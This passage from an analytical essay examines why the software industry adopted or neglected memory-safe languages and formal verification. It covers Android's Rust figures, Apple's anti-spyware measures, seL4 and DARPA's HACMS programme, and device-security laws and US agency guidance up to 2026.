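Google had counted 27 memory-safety flaws in Android by September 2024 and projected 36 for the year. The Hacker News (2025) later gave the total as fewer than 50. Memory-safety flaws fell as a share of all Android flaws partly because other flaws roughly doubled between 2019 and 2022. If other flaws had stayed at 70, memory-safety flaws would have made up about a third of the 2024 total instead of a quarter. The fall in the number of memory-safety flaws is therefore a more reliable sign of progress than the fall in their share.

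As memory-safety flaws became less common, Android's flaws also became less severe overall. In 2022, memory-safety flaws made up 36% of the total but 86% of the critical flaws and 89% of those that attackers could exploit remotely. The remaining flaws are often logic errors in Java code, such as a missing permission check. These errors usually expose one kind of data and require the attacker to have an app already on the phone.

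Rust and Java can't account for the whole fall. By the decay formula, if Android had stopped adding memory-safety flaws in 2019, the yearly number would have fallen from 223 to about 67 in 2022 and 30 in 2024. The actual figures were only slightly higher, at 85 and 36, even though Google's engineers were still adding far more C++ than Rust until 2023. Google suggests that its work on making C and C++ safer helped, including better testing tools and a safer memory allocator, the software that hands out memory to programs. Google also notes that other projects using these tools saw no comparable change in the mix of their flaws, which is evidence that the languages contributed.

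Changes in severity ratings may account for another part of the decline. About 80% of the serious media flaws in 2018 were in codecs, the programs that decode audio and video. When Google moved these into a stricter sandbox in 2019, Vander Stoep and Zhang announced that the same flaws would get a lower severity rating. Some would have dropped out of the count with no change to the code, just as flaws in switched-off services could disappear from Microsoft's bulletin totals. This might explain some of the fall in the early years, but it is a much weaker explanation for the continued decline after 2022.

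Google fixed 216 Android flaws in November 2026, 23 of them critical, according to The Hacker News' *Google Issues Patches for Critical Android Flaw That Could Allow RCE* (2026). It had fixed 25 in October (窓の杜, *2026年11月のAndroidセキュリティ情報、216件の脆弱性*, 2026). Code quality doesn't change that much in a month, so the increase must come mostly from how people looked for flaws or when Google released the fixes. The totals don't separate memory-safety flaws from others, so they can't show whether the memory-safety share kept falling.

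In December, Google fixed another 85 flaws in an update to Android 17, with no reports of attacks using them. RodHat's *Android 17 QPR2* (2026) describes one as a logic error in a video decoder that lets an attacker write outside the memory the program reserved. Android's decoders still had memory-safety flaws eleven years after Stagefright.

Google also decides which flaws are counted. Li-Yates, an independent researcher who sent Google 95 reports about its phones, alleges in *justafewbugs* (2026) that Google closed eight of them as duplicates or as not vulnerabilities, then fixed the flaws without giving credit. This is one person's account of a dispute over rewards, and flaws that Google fixes quietly could be of any kind. It is still a reason to treat the bulletins as a record of what Google chose to list.

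### Testing the "1,000 times" claim

Vander Stoep (2025) reports in *Rust in Android* that Android's Rust code has more than 1,000 times fewer memory-safety flaws per line than its C and C++ code. Android had one such flaw in about 5 million lines of Rust, or 0.2 per million lines, compared with a historical rate of about 1,000 per million for C and C++. These figures give a ratio of about 5,000.

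The one flaw was a buffer overflow in the unsafe Rust of CrabbyAVIF, software that reads images in the AVIF format. Google fixed it before any public release but gave it an official identifier, CVE-2025-48530, so that phone makers would treat the patch as urgent. Attackers could not have exploited it on most phones, because Android's allocator, Scudo, places a forbidden area of memory after each large buffer, and a program that runs into it crashes. Counting this near-miss favors C and C++ in the comparison, since the historical figure covers vulnerabilities and Rust had no released ones.

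Other parts of the comparison favour Rust. The first is the age of the code. Android had about 1.5 million lines of Rust at the end of 2022, so most of the 5 million are less than three years old, and people have had less time to find the flaws. If Google added the lines evenly and Rust flaws are found at the rate in Google's decay model, about half of the flaws would still have been hidden in late 2025, and Rust's density would be 0.4 flaws per million lines.

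The C and C++ figure also seems too high for an average. In 2022 Google reported more than one flaw per thousand lines in "many" components, naming media, Bluetooth and NFC (the short-range radio used for payments). These components handle data from untrusted sources, and researchers have studied them for years. At 1,000 flaws per million lines, even 20 million lines of C and C++ would have had 20,000 flaws, which Google would need about 90 years to list at the 2019 rate of 223 a year. Ten years at that rate would give about 110 flaws per million lines, which is probably closer to the average for serious, published flaws.

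Finding only one flaw could also be partly luck, since at the usual 95% confidence level it is consistent with an expected number as high as 5.6. The table applies these corrections one after another.

| Assumption | C and C++ flaws per million lines | Rust flaws per million lines | Ratio |
|---|---|---|---|
| Google's figures | 1,000 | 0.2 | 5,000 |
| Half of the Rust flaws are still hidden | 1,000 | 0.4 | 2,500 |
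| Lower average for C and C++ | 110 | 0.4 | 275 |
| Google was lucky to find only one Rust flaw | 110 | 2.2 | 50 |

Even with every assumption set against it, Rust comes out about 50 times safer than C++. The calculation doesn't account for how closely researchers have examined the code, which nobody has measured. They may have paid less attention to Rust components because nobody had found anything in them, but these components include attractive targets such as Android's key storage and the software that isolates virtual machines. Researchers would have to examine Rust code 50 times less closely than C++ to remove the difference. The evidence supports Rust being somewhere between tens and thousands of times safer, and the exact figure matters little for the decision to use it.

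People have found only one flaw in Android's unsafe Rust, although some programmers suspect that such code could be as dangerous as C, or worse. Unsafe blocks contain about 4% of Android's Rust, or 200,000 lines. At 110 flaws per million lines, they should contain about 22 flaws, of which people would have found about 11 by now. Vander Stoep offers several likely reasons for the difference: unsafe blocks keep most of Rust's checks, programmers wrap them in small pieces that reviewers can examine separately, and everybody looks at them more carefully. The ultra-wideband code had only two unsafe blocks in 2022, and the extra attention to them led engineers to find and prevent a possible timing bug.

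### Faster reviews and fewer rollbacks

In the first three quarters of 2025, Google's engineers added slightly more net lines of Rust than C++ to Android. Net lines are lines added minus lines deleted, so deleting old C++ lowers the C++ total. The count excludes code from other companies. Because the amounts were similar, Vander Stoep could compare development in the two languages.

| Measure | Rust compared with C++ |
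|---|---|
| Changes that engineers had to undo (rollbacks), medium and large changes | About 4 times fewer |
| Time in code review | About 25% less |
| Revisions before approval, for changes of similar size | About 20% fewer |

A rolled-back change can delay other teams and lead to an investigation and new safeguards, so the rollback rate probably matters more than the time saved in review. Vander Stoep calls the effect on development "the biggest surprise" of the move to Rust.

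The comparison is reasonably careful, since it includes only Google's own Android developers, many of whom write both languages, and groups changes by size. But a change to a ten-year-old C++ component would be riskier than a change to a new Rust one even if both were written in the same language, because more of the system depends on the old component and fewer people understand it. Engineers who chose Rust early may also have been unusually skilled or keen. The gap in review time widened between 2023 and 2024, which Vander Stoep attributes to growing experience with Rust. That suggests the first adopters' enthusiasm was not the main cause, though it doesn't rule out a difference in the kind of work. Outsiders can count the flaws in a public bulletin but can't easily repeat these comparisons, and Google has a public commitment to Rust to defend.

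If the results are even half right, they raise b, the benefit in the adoption rule that is unrelated to attacks. But Google measured these gains after 2022, so they can't have caused the 2019 decision. They help explain why Google went on to extend Rust to firmware, secure messaging and a first driver in the Linux kernel that Android uses. By November 2025, Google (2025) was presenting Rust as the obvious choice for the AirDrop link, citing both technical reasons and the approval of US security agencies.

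### Apple's response to spyware

Attacks influenced Apple more directly. In August 2016 the security firm Lookout and Citizen Lab, a research group at the University of Toronto, reported that somebody had tried to install Pegasus, spyware from the Israeli company NSO Group, on the iPhone of Ahmed Mansoor, a human rights activist in the United Arab Emirates. The spyware used three zero-days, which Apple patched about ten days after learning of them.

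In 2020 Apple added BlastDoor, a sandboxed program that reads incoming iMessages and is mostly written in Swift, Apple's memory-safe language. NSO got around it in 2021 with an exploit that Citizen Lab named FORCEDENTRY. The exploit sent a disguised file that a different program opened outside BlastDoor, then used an integer overflow in an old image decoder to compromise the phone. The victim did not have to touch anything. Apple patched the flaw that September and sued NSO in November.

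In 2022 Apple introduced Lockdown Mode, an optional setting that blocks most kinds of message attachment, turns off link previews and disables some features that speed up web pages. Apple recommends it only for the few people spyware companies are likely to target, such as journalists and dissidents. It reduces what an attacker can reach without fixing any flaws, and most users would find it too inconvenient to keep on.

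With Memory Integrity Enforcement, which Apple introduced with the iPhone 17 in September 2025, the processor gives each 16-byte piece of memory a secret tag, and a program must present the matching tag to use it. If a program reads past the end of a message, as OpenSSL did with Heartbleed, it soon reaches memory with a different tag and the processor stops it. Apple described five years of work on the system, and said the only system-level attacks on iPhones it had seen in practice came from spyware that costs millions of dollars and targets very few people. So attacks on a few people led, at least in part, to a defence for everyone who buys the new phones.

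The defence counts as hardening because the flaws are still in the C code, but it protects old code without a rewrite. Apple was well placed to build it because it designs both the processor and the operating system. Google has worked with chip makers on similar tags for Android, but other companies make most Android phones and choose the processors.

Both companies' security teams have used exploit prices to judge how well their defences work, since attackers should have to pay more for exploits that are harder to write. Google's Android security director used this measure in a Stanford lecture, *Android Security* (Mayrhofer 2019), and Kralevich had used it two years earlier. Kralevich also cited prizes from the 2016 Mobile Pwn2Own hacking contest, which offered $125,000 for installing a rogue app on an iPhone, $100,000 on Google's Nexus and $60,000 on other Android phones. In 2017 Google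 raised its own top reward from $50,000 to $200,000 after nobody had claimed it for two years. Brokers, who buy exploits to sell to governments, advertised much higher prices.

| Date | Broker | Top price, iPhone | Top price, Android |
|---|---|---|---|
| November 2015 | Zerodium | $0.5m | $0.1m |
| September 2016 | Zerodium | $1.5m | $0.2m |
| September 2019 | Zerodium | $2m | $2.5m |
| April 2024 | Crowdfense | $5m–7m | $5m |

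The price brokers offered for an Android exploit rose more than twelvefold between 2016 and 2019, before any version of Android with Rust support had come out. If defences caused the rise, it was the hardening after Stagefright that did so. But these prices are advertised offers, not records of sales, and the brokers did not always ask for the same kind of exploit. Prices also depend on how much governments want to spy on phones and how many exploits are for sale. Zerodium's founder said in 2019 that iPhone exploits had flooded the market. All four offers predate the AI bug-finding of 2026, which may have made exploits much cheaper to produce.

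## The seL4 kernel and the slow uptake of verified software

Rust prevents one class of flaw, while formal verification can prevent almost every kind of coding mistake. In July 2009 researchers in Sydney finished the first formal verification of a general-purpose operating-system kernel, seL4. Heartbleed, WannaCry and Log4Shell all came later, so if attacks push industry towards safer software, seL4 should have spread, but 17 years on it runs in a few specialised products.

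### Why researchers chose the kernel

A kernel is the part of an operating system that runs in the processor's most privileged mode. It has unlimited access to the hardware, so a single flaw in it can expose every program on the machine. seL4 is a microkernel, which keeps only the functions that need the privilege, such as controlling access to memory and passing messages between programs. The file system and the drivers, which operate devices such as network cards, run outside it as ordinary programs. seL4 therefore needed 8,700 lines of C and 600 of assembly language, while the Linux kernel has about 40 million lines of code.

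Researchers were trying to verify kernels before the internet worms. *seL4* (Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues, 2009) describes an attempt at UCLA in the 1970s that completed 90% of its specification and 20% of its proofs in five person-years. The simplifications it needed made the kernel about ten times slower. The seL4 team, based in Sydney at NICTA, a research centre funded by the Australian government, aimed to lose no more than 10% in speed, according to the seL4 Foundation, which now looks after the project. In early measurements seL4 took 224 processor cycles to pass a message, compared with 206 for a hand-tuned rival.

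### From specification to machine code

The team described the kernel at three levels of detail. In the abstract specification, for example, the scheduler, which decides which program runs next, may choose any program that is ready to run. The executable specification, which a tool produced from a prototype written in Haskell, requires the kernel to keep a queue for each priority and take the next program from the highest-priority queue that isn't empty. The C code follows the same method, using pointers and tightly packed data for speed.

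Klein and colleagues then proved that each level refines the one above it, meaning that it never does anything the higher level rules out. Let R be a relation that pairs a state of the C kernel, s, with a state of the specification, σ. The proof establishes that

if R(σ, s) holds and the C code can go from s to s′, then the specification can go from σ to some σ′ for which R(σ′, s′) holds.

A kernel that starts in a matching state therefore stays in matching states as it runs. The team wrote the proof in Isabelle/HOL, a program that checks every step. The proof's model lets user programs do anything, so the result covers malicious programs as well as buggy ones. No request can crash the kernel, trap it in an endless loop or overflow one of its buffers.

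Most of the work went into more than 150 invariants, facts that must hold before and after every request. For example, each item's back link in a two-way linked list must point to the item before it. Any part of the kernel that writes to memory could break such a list, so the team had to check each invariant against the whole kernel.

The 2009 proof stopped at the C code, so a faulty compiler could still have produced a faulty kernel. *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel* (Klein, Andronick and colleagues, 2014) describes closing that gap with a separate tool that proves the compiled program behaves as the C code should. The tool found no errors made by the compiler. The team also proved that the specification guarantees integrity, meaning a program cannot change data without permission, and confidentiality, meaning it cannot learn about another program without permission.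 To prove confidentiality, they had to alter the scheduler, because programs could have signalled to each other through its decisions.

The proofs also assume that the processor works as its manual describes, and that the boot code, handwritten assembly and cache management are correct. An attacker can sometimes make hardware misbehave, for instance by reading one area of memory so often that bits flip in the next. The proofs don't cover timing, so a program might still learn a secret by measuring how long an operation takes. They apply to a single processor core. Gernot Heiser, a professor at the University of New South Wales (UNSW) who founded the group that built the kernel, described work on several cores as still in progress in March (*seL4*, 2026).

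Independent testing of CompCert, a C compiler with a proof that its output matches its input, gives evidence of where flaws turn up in verified software. A research group built a tool that tests compilers with random programs and used it to find 325 bugs in various C compilers. The bugs in CompCert were all in parts the proof did not cover or in its description of the hardware. Six processor-years of testing found no errors in the proved part, according to *The HACMS program* (Fisher, Launchbury and Richards, 2017).

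### What the proof cost

A person-year is one person's work for a year. The 2014 paper gives these totals:

| Work | Person-years |
|---|---|
| Designing and writing the kernel | 2.2 |
| Reusable proof tools and libraries | 9 |
| Specifications and proof specific to seL4 | 11 |
| Proof for a faster way of passing messages | 0.4 |
| Integrity proof | 0.6 |
| Confidentiality proof | 3.4 |
| Proof about the compiled program | 2 |

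The usual figure of 20 person-years for verifying seL4 includes building the tools as well as writing the proof. The proof had about 200,000 lines in 2009, or 23 for each line of C, and has since grown to more than a million. The team expected a similar kernel to take 8 person-years, including 6 for the proof, because later projects could reuse the tools. A conventional kernel of that size would take about 4 person-years.

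The seL4 kernel and its first proof cost little by the standards of large software companies. Klein and colleagues (2014) put the cost at $362 a line, or about $3.1 million. Microsoft spent over 30 times as much on its halt in Windows development. The 2009 paper made the proof look even cheaper by comparison, because it gave the industry's rule of thumb for a high-level security certificate as $10,000 a line. The 2014 paper corrected this to $1,000 and called the earlier figure an "embarrassing typo".

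The money paid for many repairs as well as for prevention. Testing and use by students had found 16 defects in the C code, and the proof found another 144. Most were simple mistakes, such as typos, but many could have crashed the kernel or let an attacker in. The testing had been fairly light, so a commercial test team would have found more than 16.

Two problems are harder for a company to accept. First, changing a verified product takes a lot of work. One new feature altered less than 5% of the kernel's code, but redoing the proof took a person-year, 17% of the original effort. Second, the effort of verification seems to grow with the square of a program's size, because each new part can break the invariants of all the others. By that rule, if a 10,000-line kernel takes 8 person-years, Linux, at 4,000 times the size, would take 8 × 4,000², or 128 million person-years. The rule is based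 on very little data. Splitting a program into ten independent modules could in theory cut the effort to a tenth, but Linux was not built that way.

### Hacked cars and a helicopter

The largest attempt to use seL4 outside the laboratory was High-Assurance Cyber Military Systems (HACMS), a programme that DARPA, the US military's research agency, ran from 2012 to 2017. Fisher and colleagues, who managed it, use cars as their main example of the danger of hacking. In 2010 the computer scientists Tadayoshi Kohno and Stefan Savage showed that anyone who plugged into the diagnostic port under a car's steering wheel could replace the software on every computer in the car, including those that control the brakes.

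A year later they did it without touching the car. One method exploited a flawed `strcpy` call in the Bluetooth code, the C function from the greeting program. Another took an average of 128 phone calls to the car's built-in mobile connection, and a third hid an attack in a song that played normally on a PC. In 2015, when HACMS was well under way, two other researchers disabled the transmission of a Jeep on a highway with a reporter at the wheel, and the maker recalled 1.4 million vehicles. Fisher and colleagues say the Jeep demonstration showed no fundamentally new weakness.

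These were researchers' demonstrations, so HACMS, like Android's monthly updates, responded to a warning rather than a loss. The danger was only part of the reason for it. The managers write that seL4 and CompCert were crucial to DARPA's decision because they gave some confidence that the programme could succeed.

DARPA hired professional hackers as a "red team" to attack two aircraft: a small quadcopter, which researchers could modify freely, and Boeing's Unmanned Little Bird, a helicopter that can fly with or without a pilot. It gave the hackers the source code and documents, and six weeks at a time to attack each aircraft.

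| Test | What the red team started with | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Original quadcopter | Source code and documents | Took control of it in flight |
| Original helicopter, 2013 | Source code and documents | Could have crashed or diverted it |
| Quadcopter after 16 months | Source code, attacks by radio only | Did not break in |
| Both aircraft, second phase | Administrator control of the Linux section | Destroyed the camera software but could not leave that section or disturb the flight |
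| Helicopter in flight, February 2017 | Rogue camera software and an infected USB stick | Compromised some subsystems; the helicopter flew safely |

seL4 had no part in the first successful defence. The researchers had rewritten much of the quadcopter's software in Ivory, a restricted language that generates memory-safe C, and proved that the aircraft would discard any message without valid credentials. This was prevention by safer language and stricter input checks, much like Android's. seL4 arrived in the second phase, when the question became how to contain software that nobody had time to rewrite.

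*Formally Verified Software in the Real World* describes how Boeing rebuilt the helicopter's mission computer, which communicated with the ground and handled the camera. All of its software originally ran as one program on Linux. The engineers first moved that program, unchanged, into a virtual machine (a simulated computer) running on seL4. This step alone added no security. They then split the program into separate virtual machines for ground communication and camera navigation, and moved the network connection into its own component. Finally, they rewrote the communication, encryption and mission-planning code in the language Ivory and left the camera and Wi-Fi in a Linux virtual machine that they expected to have vulnerabilities. An attacker who took over the camera could send false data to the mission planner, which checked the data, but the attacker could reach nothing else.

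Boeing engineers did most of this work, which is evidence against the objection that only specialists can use a verified kernel, though the kernel's developers worked with them as partners. The safety pilot noticed no difference in handling. The testers excluded radio jamming and hardware attacks and assumed that the encryption was sound. The argument linking seL4's proofs to the safety of the whole aircraft was informal, and the network component was written in ordinary C.

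Fisher and colleagues hoped that military buyers would start requiring proofs, and that suppliers would then reuse their new skills in civilian products such as insulin pumps. Congress took a much smaller step, which still let suppliers win contracts without a proof. Fisher reports in *Formal Methods at Scale* that the programme's success led to a clause in the defence authorisation act of 2018 telling the Pentagon to study such methods.

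### Who uses seL4, and who stopped paying for it

seL4 was not freely available at first. The research group had set up a company, Open Kernel Labs, in 2006, and the defence contractor General Dynamics bought it in 2012. Researchers could download only a compiled version of the kernel until its owners released the source code in 2014, so the period in which any company could have built on it is nearer 12 years than 17. In 2020 the developers created the seL4 Foundation, whose early members included the security firm HENSOLDT Cyber and the engineering company DornerWorks.

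A year later the developers lost their main sponsor. CSIRO, the Australian national research agency that had absorbed NICTA, disbanded the team in May 2021 during a restructuring that threatened up to 70 jobs. A spokesperson told iTnews that verification was "a mature area of technology" with enough support elsewhere (*Data61 dismantles research group behind seL4 secure OS*). According to InnovationAus' *CSIRO boss explains why seL4 team was dumped*, the agency's chief executive, Larry Marshall, attributed the decision to a new focus on AI and the difficulty of building an Australian industry on the technology. Several of the leading proof experts had already left to found a company. Also in May 2021, criminals forced the closure of the Colonial Pipeline, which carries much of the fuel for the US East Coast.

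UNSW provided six months of funding, and by July the team was back at the university. A research council grant paid for extending the proofs to another family of processors. Many people consider the project the best in its field, yet it had nearly lost its staff over a budget that would be small for a mid-sized software company.

By 2026 seL4 was in real products. The Chinese carmaker NIO has used it in its electric cars since the ONVO L60 of 2024, and Heiser reports that national security systems use it too. The voice system that air-traffic and maritime controllers use to talk to pilots and captains also runs on seL4. Its maker, MEP, chose seL4 to guarantee round-the-clock service, according to the seL4 Foundation's *seL4 is used across a wide range of sectors*. That choice was as much about reliability, which is part of b in the adoption rule, as about security. A Swiss start-up, Neutrality,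 is developing a system on seL4 for data centres that expect well-resourced attackers, which is closer to a response to attacks. The Foundation's list is promotional, and it notes that many uses are secret, so the exact number is unknown.

Heiser compares seL4 to an assembly language for operating systems. It has no file system, networking or drivers, so product builders must supply them. Most successful projects so far either worked closely with the kernel's creators or hired several UNSW graduates, and Heiser writes that the difficulty of building on seL4 is "clearly inhibiting" uptake. *The seL4 Microkernel* (2024), a paper for builders of military ground vehicles, makes the same complaint and adds that proving the missing parts correct can be prohibitively expensive.

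### Verified isolation at Google and Amazon

Large companies have since built verified or partly verified isolation software. Google's pKVM, which first shipped with Android 13 in 2022, is a small hypervisor, a program that runs several operating systems on one machine and keeps them apart. Google wanted phones to protect sensitive data and AI models even if an attacker took over Android's main kernel, Linux, which is far too large to verify.

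pKVM has no complete proof. Researchers at Cambridge and elsewhere worked with Google on an exact specification of it and on proving one component, the memory allocator. For the rest, the specification serves as a test oracle: while the hypervisor runs its tests, a program checks whether the specification allows each thing it does. Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod, who took part in this work, recommend the method as a cheap first step towards proof, since it finds mistakes in code and specification alike and needs no unusual tools.

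Amazon went further for its cloud service, where rival companies' programs run on the same machine. In December 2025 it announced the Nitro Isolation Engine, a small component that separates customers' virtual machines on its newest servers, with a proof of that separation in Isabelle. Amazon said it wanted to assure customers that neither other customers nor its own staff could reach their data. If one customer broke into another's virtual machine, many others might leave, so Amazon bears a much larger share of the loss than the maker of a desktop program would.

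In earlier work, Amazon's engineers had also found that verification made them think more clearly about designs and gave them the confidence to speed up code in ways they would otherwise have thought too risky (*How Could Formal Verification Help with Cyber Resilience?*). At Amazon's scale, events that happen once in a million requests happen every second, so rare design errors that testing misses are expensive even without an attacker. One engineer who wanted colleagues to try these methods avoided the word "formal" and called them "exhaustively testable pseudo-code".

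Verified code has spread furthest where its users did not have to change anything. Since about 2018, BoringSSL, Google's fork of OpenSSL, has included verified arithmetic routines, which everyone who uses Chrome runs. miTLS, a verified replacement for the part of OpenSSL that sets up encrypted connections, took a decade to develop and has few users. Its interface differs from OpenSSL's, so developers would have to rewrite their programs to adopt it.

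### Did attack pressure ever have a usable option?

The simplest reading of this history is that attack pressure failed. Companies had a verified kernel available, heard about a new disaster every year or two, and kept building on Linux and Windows. Kleppmann (2025), in *Prediction*, gives an economic explanation, which is that for most systems the expected cost of bugs is lower than the cost of the proofs that would prevent them. Fisher and colleagues think that verification might become a very good investment if the law made companies in certain industries pay for damage caused by their flawed code.

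Supporters of verification reply that companies never had a practical product to switch to. Proofs took rare experts years, the kernel came without drivers, and hardly any customers could insist on verified software. DARPA's HACMS programme partly supports this view. With DARPA as a wealthy and demanding buyer, Boeing had a rebuilt helicopter flying within a few years, but the demand ended with the programme.

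Some supporters also blame their own field. Martin Dehnel-Wild of Kry10, which sells an operating system based on seL4, argues in the seL4 Foundation's *seL4 Summit 2026 Abstracts* (2026) that the remaining obstacles are "largely self-inflicted". He lists exaggerated promises, painful tools and a habit of staying in the laboratory. Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod add that some early champions of proof presented it as a replacement for testing, which put off engineers who relied on tests.

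A verified kernel would also have done less against the famous attacks than its supporters sometimes imply. The file-sharing code that WannaCry exploited would have run outside seL4 as an ordinary program, so the attackers would have controlled that program and not the whole machine. But the program needs access to the shared files, so the ransomware could still have encrypted them. The criminals who broke into MOVEit wanted the data that the vulnerable program handled. Isolation helps most where a small critical function, such as flying a helicopter, can run apart from everything else. For an ordinary office, r, the share of the loss that the practice prevents, is much lower, so declining to move to seL4 was probably sensible.

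That excuse is weaker for cars, medical devices and industrial controllers, which resemble the helicopter. For these products the missing parts were a real obstacle, but a fairly cheap one to remove. LionsOS, a free operating system that Heiser's group has built on seL4, has a fast driver for one common network chip that a second-year student wrote in 569 lines of code. The Linux version has 4,775. Where nobody has written a new driver, LionsOS can run the Linux one in a virtual machine, as Boeing did with its camera. After 2014 the work needed steady funding for a few dozen engineers rather than a scientific breakthrough, but the companies that would have benefited had the same reason to wait for one another as OpenSSL's users did before Heartbleed.

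AI is now changing how much work proofs take, independently of any attacks. Kleppmann predicted in December 2025 that AI would write most proofs and bring verification into ordinary software development. By October 2026 Anthropic's Claude had written proofs for 123 open-source libraries, though these covered much narrower properties than seL4's. Sewell and Pichon-Pharabod warn that even proofs that take little effort need exact descriptions of the languages and hardware underneath. C has no specification language nearly as well established as C itself, and no single company would gain enough from one to pay for it alone.

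## Government guidance, pledges and laws, 2016–2026

In 2016, attackers used badly protected cameras and routers to cut off large websites. Governments have since moved some way towards the legal liability that the managers of DARPA's helicopter programme wanted. But the first laws dealt with simple faults such as default passwords. For memory safety, US agencies have relied on advice that companies can ignore.

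### How Mirai used default passwords

In autumn 2016 a program called Mirai took over hundreds of thousands of internet-connected cameras, video recorders and home routers. It searched the internet for devices that accepted remote logins and tried about 60 common username and password pairs, such as "admin" and "admin". It needed no exploit, because makers had shipped every unit of a model with the same login. On some devices the owner could not change the password, because the maker had fixed it in the built-in software.

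Mirai's creators published its code at the end of September, and others soon built their own botnets, which are groups of infected machines under one person's control. On 21 October attackers used Mirai to flood Dyn, a company that directed internet users to the right servers, and for several hours many Americans could not reach Twitter, Netflix or Reddit.

The cameras used in the Mirai attack on Dyn kept working. Their owners lost a little bandwidth, while Dyn and its customers lost business. One Chinese manufacturer, Xiongmai, recalled some of its webcams from the US market, but most makers lost nothing. Microsoft had changed after the worms of 2001 largely because they hurt its own customers. Mirai's victims were not the camera makers' customers, so the makers' share of the loss, s, was close to zero, and more attacks would hardly have changed their behaviour.

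### Laws in California, Britain and the EU

| Law | Adopted | Makers must comply from | Covers | Maximum fine |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| California's SB-327 | September 2018 | January 2020 | Connected devices sold in California | None stated |
| Britain's Product Security and Telecommunications Infrastructure Act | December 2022 | April 2024 | Most connected consumer devices | £10m or 4% of worldwide revenue, whichever is higher |
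| EU Cyber Resilience Act | October 2024 | September 2026 for reporting, December 2027 for the rest | Nearly all connected hardware and software | €15m or 2.5% of worldwide turnover, whichever is higher |

SB-327 requires makers to give each connected device "reasonable" security features suited to what it does. A device that people can log in to from outside the local network meets the standard if each unit has its own password, or if the user must set a new one before first use. Only public lawyers such as the state's attorney general can enforce the law, and no prominent case under it appears to have reached the courts. Mirai was one motive for the law, but the first version of the bill, in early 2017, dealt largely with toys and appliances that quietly collected information about their owners.

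In October 2018 the British government published a voluntary code of practice with 13 guidelines for makers of connected devices. The first was to remove default passwords, and the second was to give the public a way to report security flaws. The IoT Security Foundation, an industry body, found that about 10% of consumer device makers offered a way to report flaws in 2018 and about 27% in 2022. The government had decided well before 2022 that the code was not enough.

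The British law made three of the 13 guidelines compulsory. Makers may not use the same default password on every unit, must publish a contact for reporting flaws, and must state how long they will provide security updates. The law sets no minimum for that period, so a maker can promise a very short one as long as it says so publicly. Publishing the period addresses the lemons problem, since buyers can now compare products on at least one aspect of security. When the law took effect, ministers named Mirai as an example of the attacks it should prevent.

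The Cyber Resilience Act goes much further. Makers must assess a product's security risks, ship it with secure default settings and without known exploitable flaws, and keep a list of the software components it contains. They must also provide security updates, normally for at least five years. Since September 2026 they have had to warn the authorities within 24 hours of learning that attackers are using a flaw in their product. When proposing the law in 2022, the European Commission cited WannaCry, the Pegasus spyware and a 2021 ransomware attack that spread through the software company Kaseya.

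The act covers ordinary software, including file-transfer programs like MOVEit. It also affects free libraries, whose neglect Heartbleed exposed. A company that builds one into its product must check it with due care, report any flaw it finds to the maintainers, and share any fix it writes. The act does not require a memory-safe language. It calls for makers to limit the attack surface and to reduce the impact of incidents with hardening techniques, which make exploitation more difficult. Most makers will assess their own compliance, much as vendors under the Common Criteria could choose their own evaluators.

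A separate EU directive on product liability, which member states must apply from 9 December 2026, treats software as a product. People harmed by a defective program will be able to claim compensation without proving negligence. This raises s more directly than a fine does, but only individuals can claim, not businesses that lose money in an attack.

### What a fine adds to the adoption rule

A fine adds another benefit to the left side of the adoption rule, equal to the yearly chance of a fine multiplied by its size. Suppose it would cost a camera maker £200,000 a year to give every unit its own password, and attacks using its cameras cost it nothing. Without a law, it has no reason to spend the money. If the fine is £10 million, a 2% chance each year of having to pay it is enough to justify the spending.

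The same fine would justify a £5 million rewrite in a memory-safe language only if the maker faced a 50% chance of paying it. A rewrite would also be much harder for inspectors to check. Anyone who buys two cameras can compare their passwords, but customers and inspectors usually can't see a product's source code. Laws against default passwords were therefore an easy place to start, and their success would not show that a similar law could make companies replace C++.

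### Have default passwords become rarer?

There is no good data on this over time. Jack Cable, an adviser at CISA, the US cybersecurity agency, said in The Record's *CISA's Jack Cable on secure-by-design pledge progress* that no single source could show how many companies' products still had default passwords. The agency relied on what companies chose to publish.

The best evidence that the laws had an effect comes from individual products. For years the Raspberry Pi, a cheap computer popular with hobbyists, came with the username "pi" and the password "raspberry". In April 2022 its makers removed this login and made users create their own, explaining that some countries were introducing laws against default logins. The British law did not pass until eight months later, so the prospect of a law was enough to prompt the change.

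Default passwords remained common elsewhere. In November 2023 hackers linked to Iran broke into industrial controllers at American water utilities. Many of the controllers still used the default password, "1111". The maker, Unitronics, then released an update that forced users to change it. The British law would not have applied to controllers sold to utilities, because it covers consumer products.

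Even perfect compliance would take years to noticeably reduce the number of vulnerable devices. If owners replace a seventh of their devices each year, about two-thirds of those in use when the British law took effect in April 2024 would still be running in December 2026. A ban on default passwords would also have done little against Aisuru, a botnet that grew mainly by exploiting flaws in routers and cameras and by tampering with one router maker's updates. Aisuru was behind attacks of about 30 terabits per second in 2025, roughly 30 times the size of the largest Mirai attacks.

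### What US agencies advised on memory safety

The National Security Agency issued the first major US advice on memory safety in November 2022, and four more documents followed. According to WA SOC's *NSA* (2022), a summary from the Western Australian government's security centre, the agency advised organisations to "consider making a strategic shift" to memory-safe languages when possible.

| Date | Document | Addressed to | Main request |
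|---|---|---|---|
| November 2022 | NSA advice on memory safety | Organisations that write or use software | Consider moving to memory-safe languages |
| December 2023 | *The Case for Memory Safe Roadmaps* | Senior executives of software makers | Publish a plan for removing memory-safety flaws |
| February 2024 | *Back to the Building Blocks* (White House) | Software and hardware makers, researchers | Adopt memory-safe languages and find better ways to measure software security |
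| October 2024, revised January 2025 | *Product Security Bad Practices* | Makers of software, especially for critical infrastructure | Publish a memory-safety roadmap by 1 January 2026 |
| June 2025 | *Memory Safe Languages* (CISA and NSA) | Universities, government and companies | Support and plan the move to memory-safe languages |

None of this guidance carried a penalty. CISA and seven other agencies from the United States, Australia, Canada, New Zealand and Britain wrote *The Case for Memory Safe Roadmaps* (2023). They described memory safety as a matter of business strategy, so they wanted the chief executive or another business executive to sign the company's roadmap. They also wanted the roadmap to set dates for each phase, and a date after which the company would write new code only in a memory-safe language.

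The agencies' technical advice was close to what Google had been doing with Android. They advised companies to start with small new projects, then replace self-contained parts of old products, giving priority to code that handles untrusted data or secret keys. A team can run the old and new versions of a component side by side until their results agree. The agencies admitted that the change would take significant investment over several years, and that even new Rust programs would have to rely on old C libraries for the foreseeable future.

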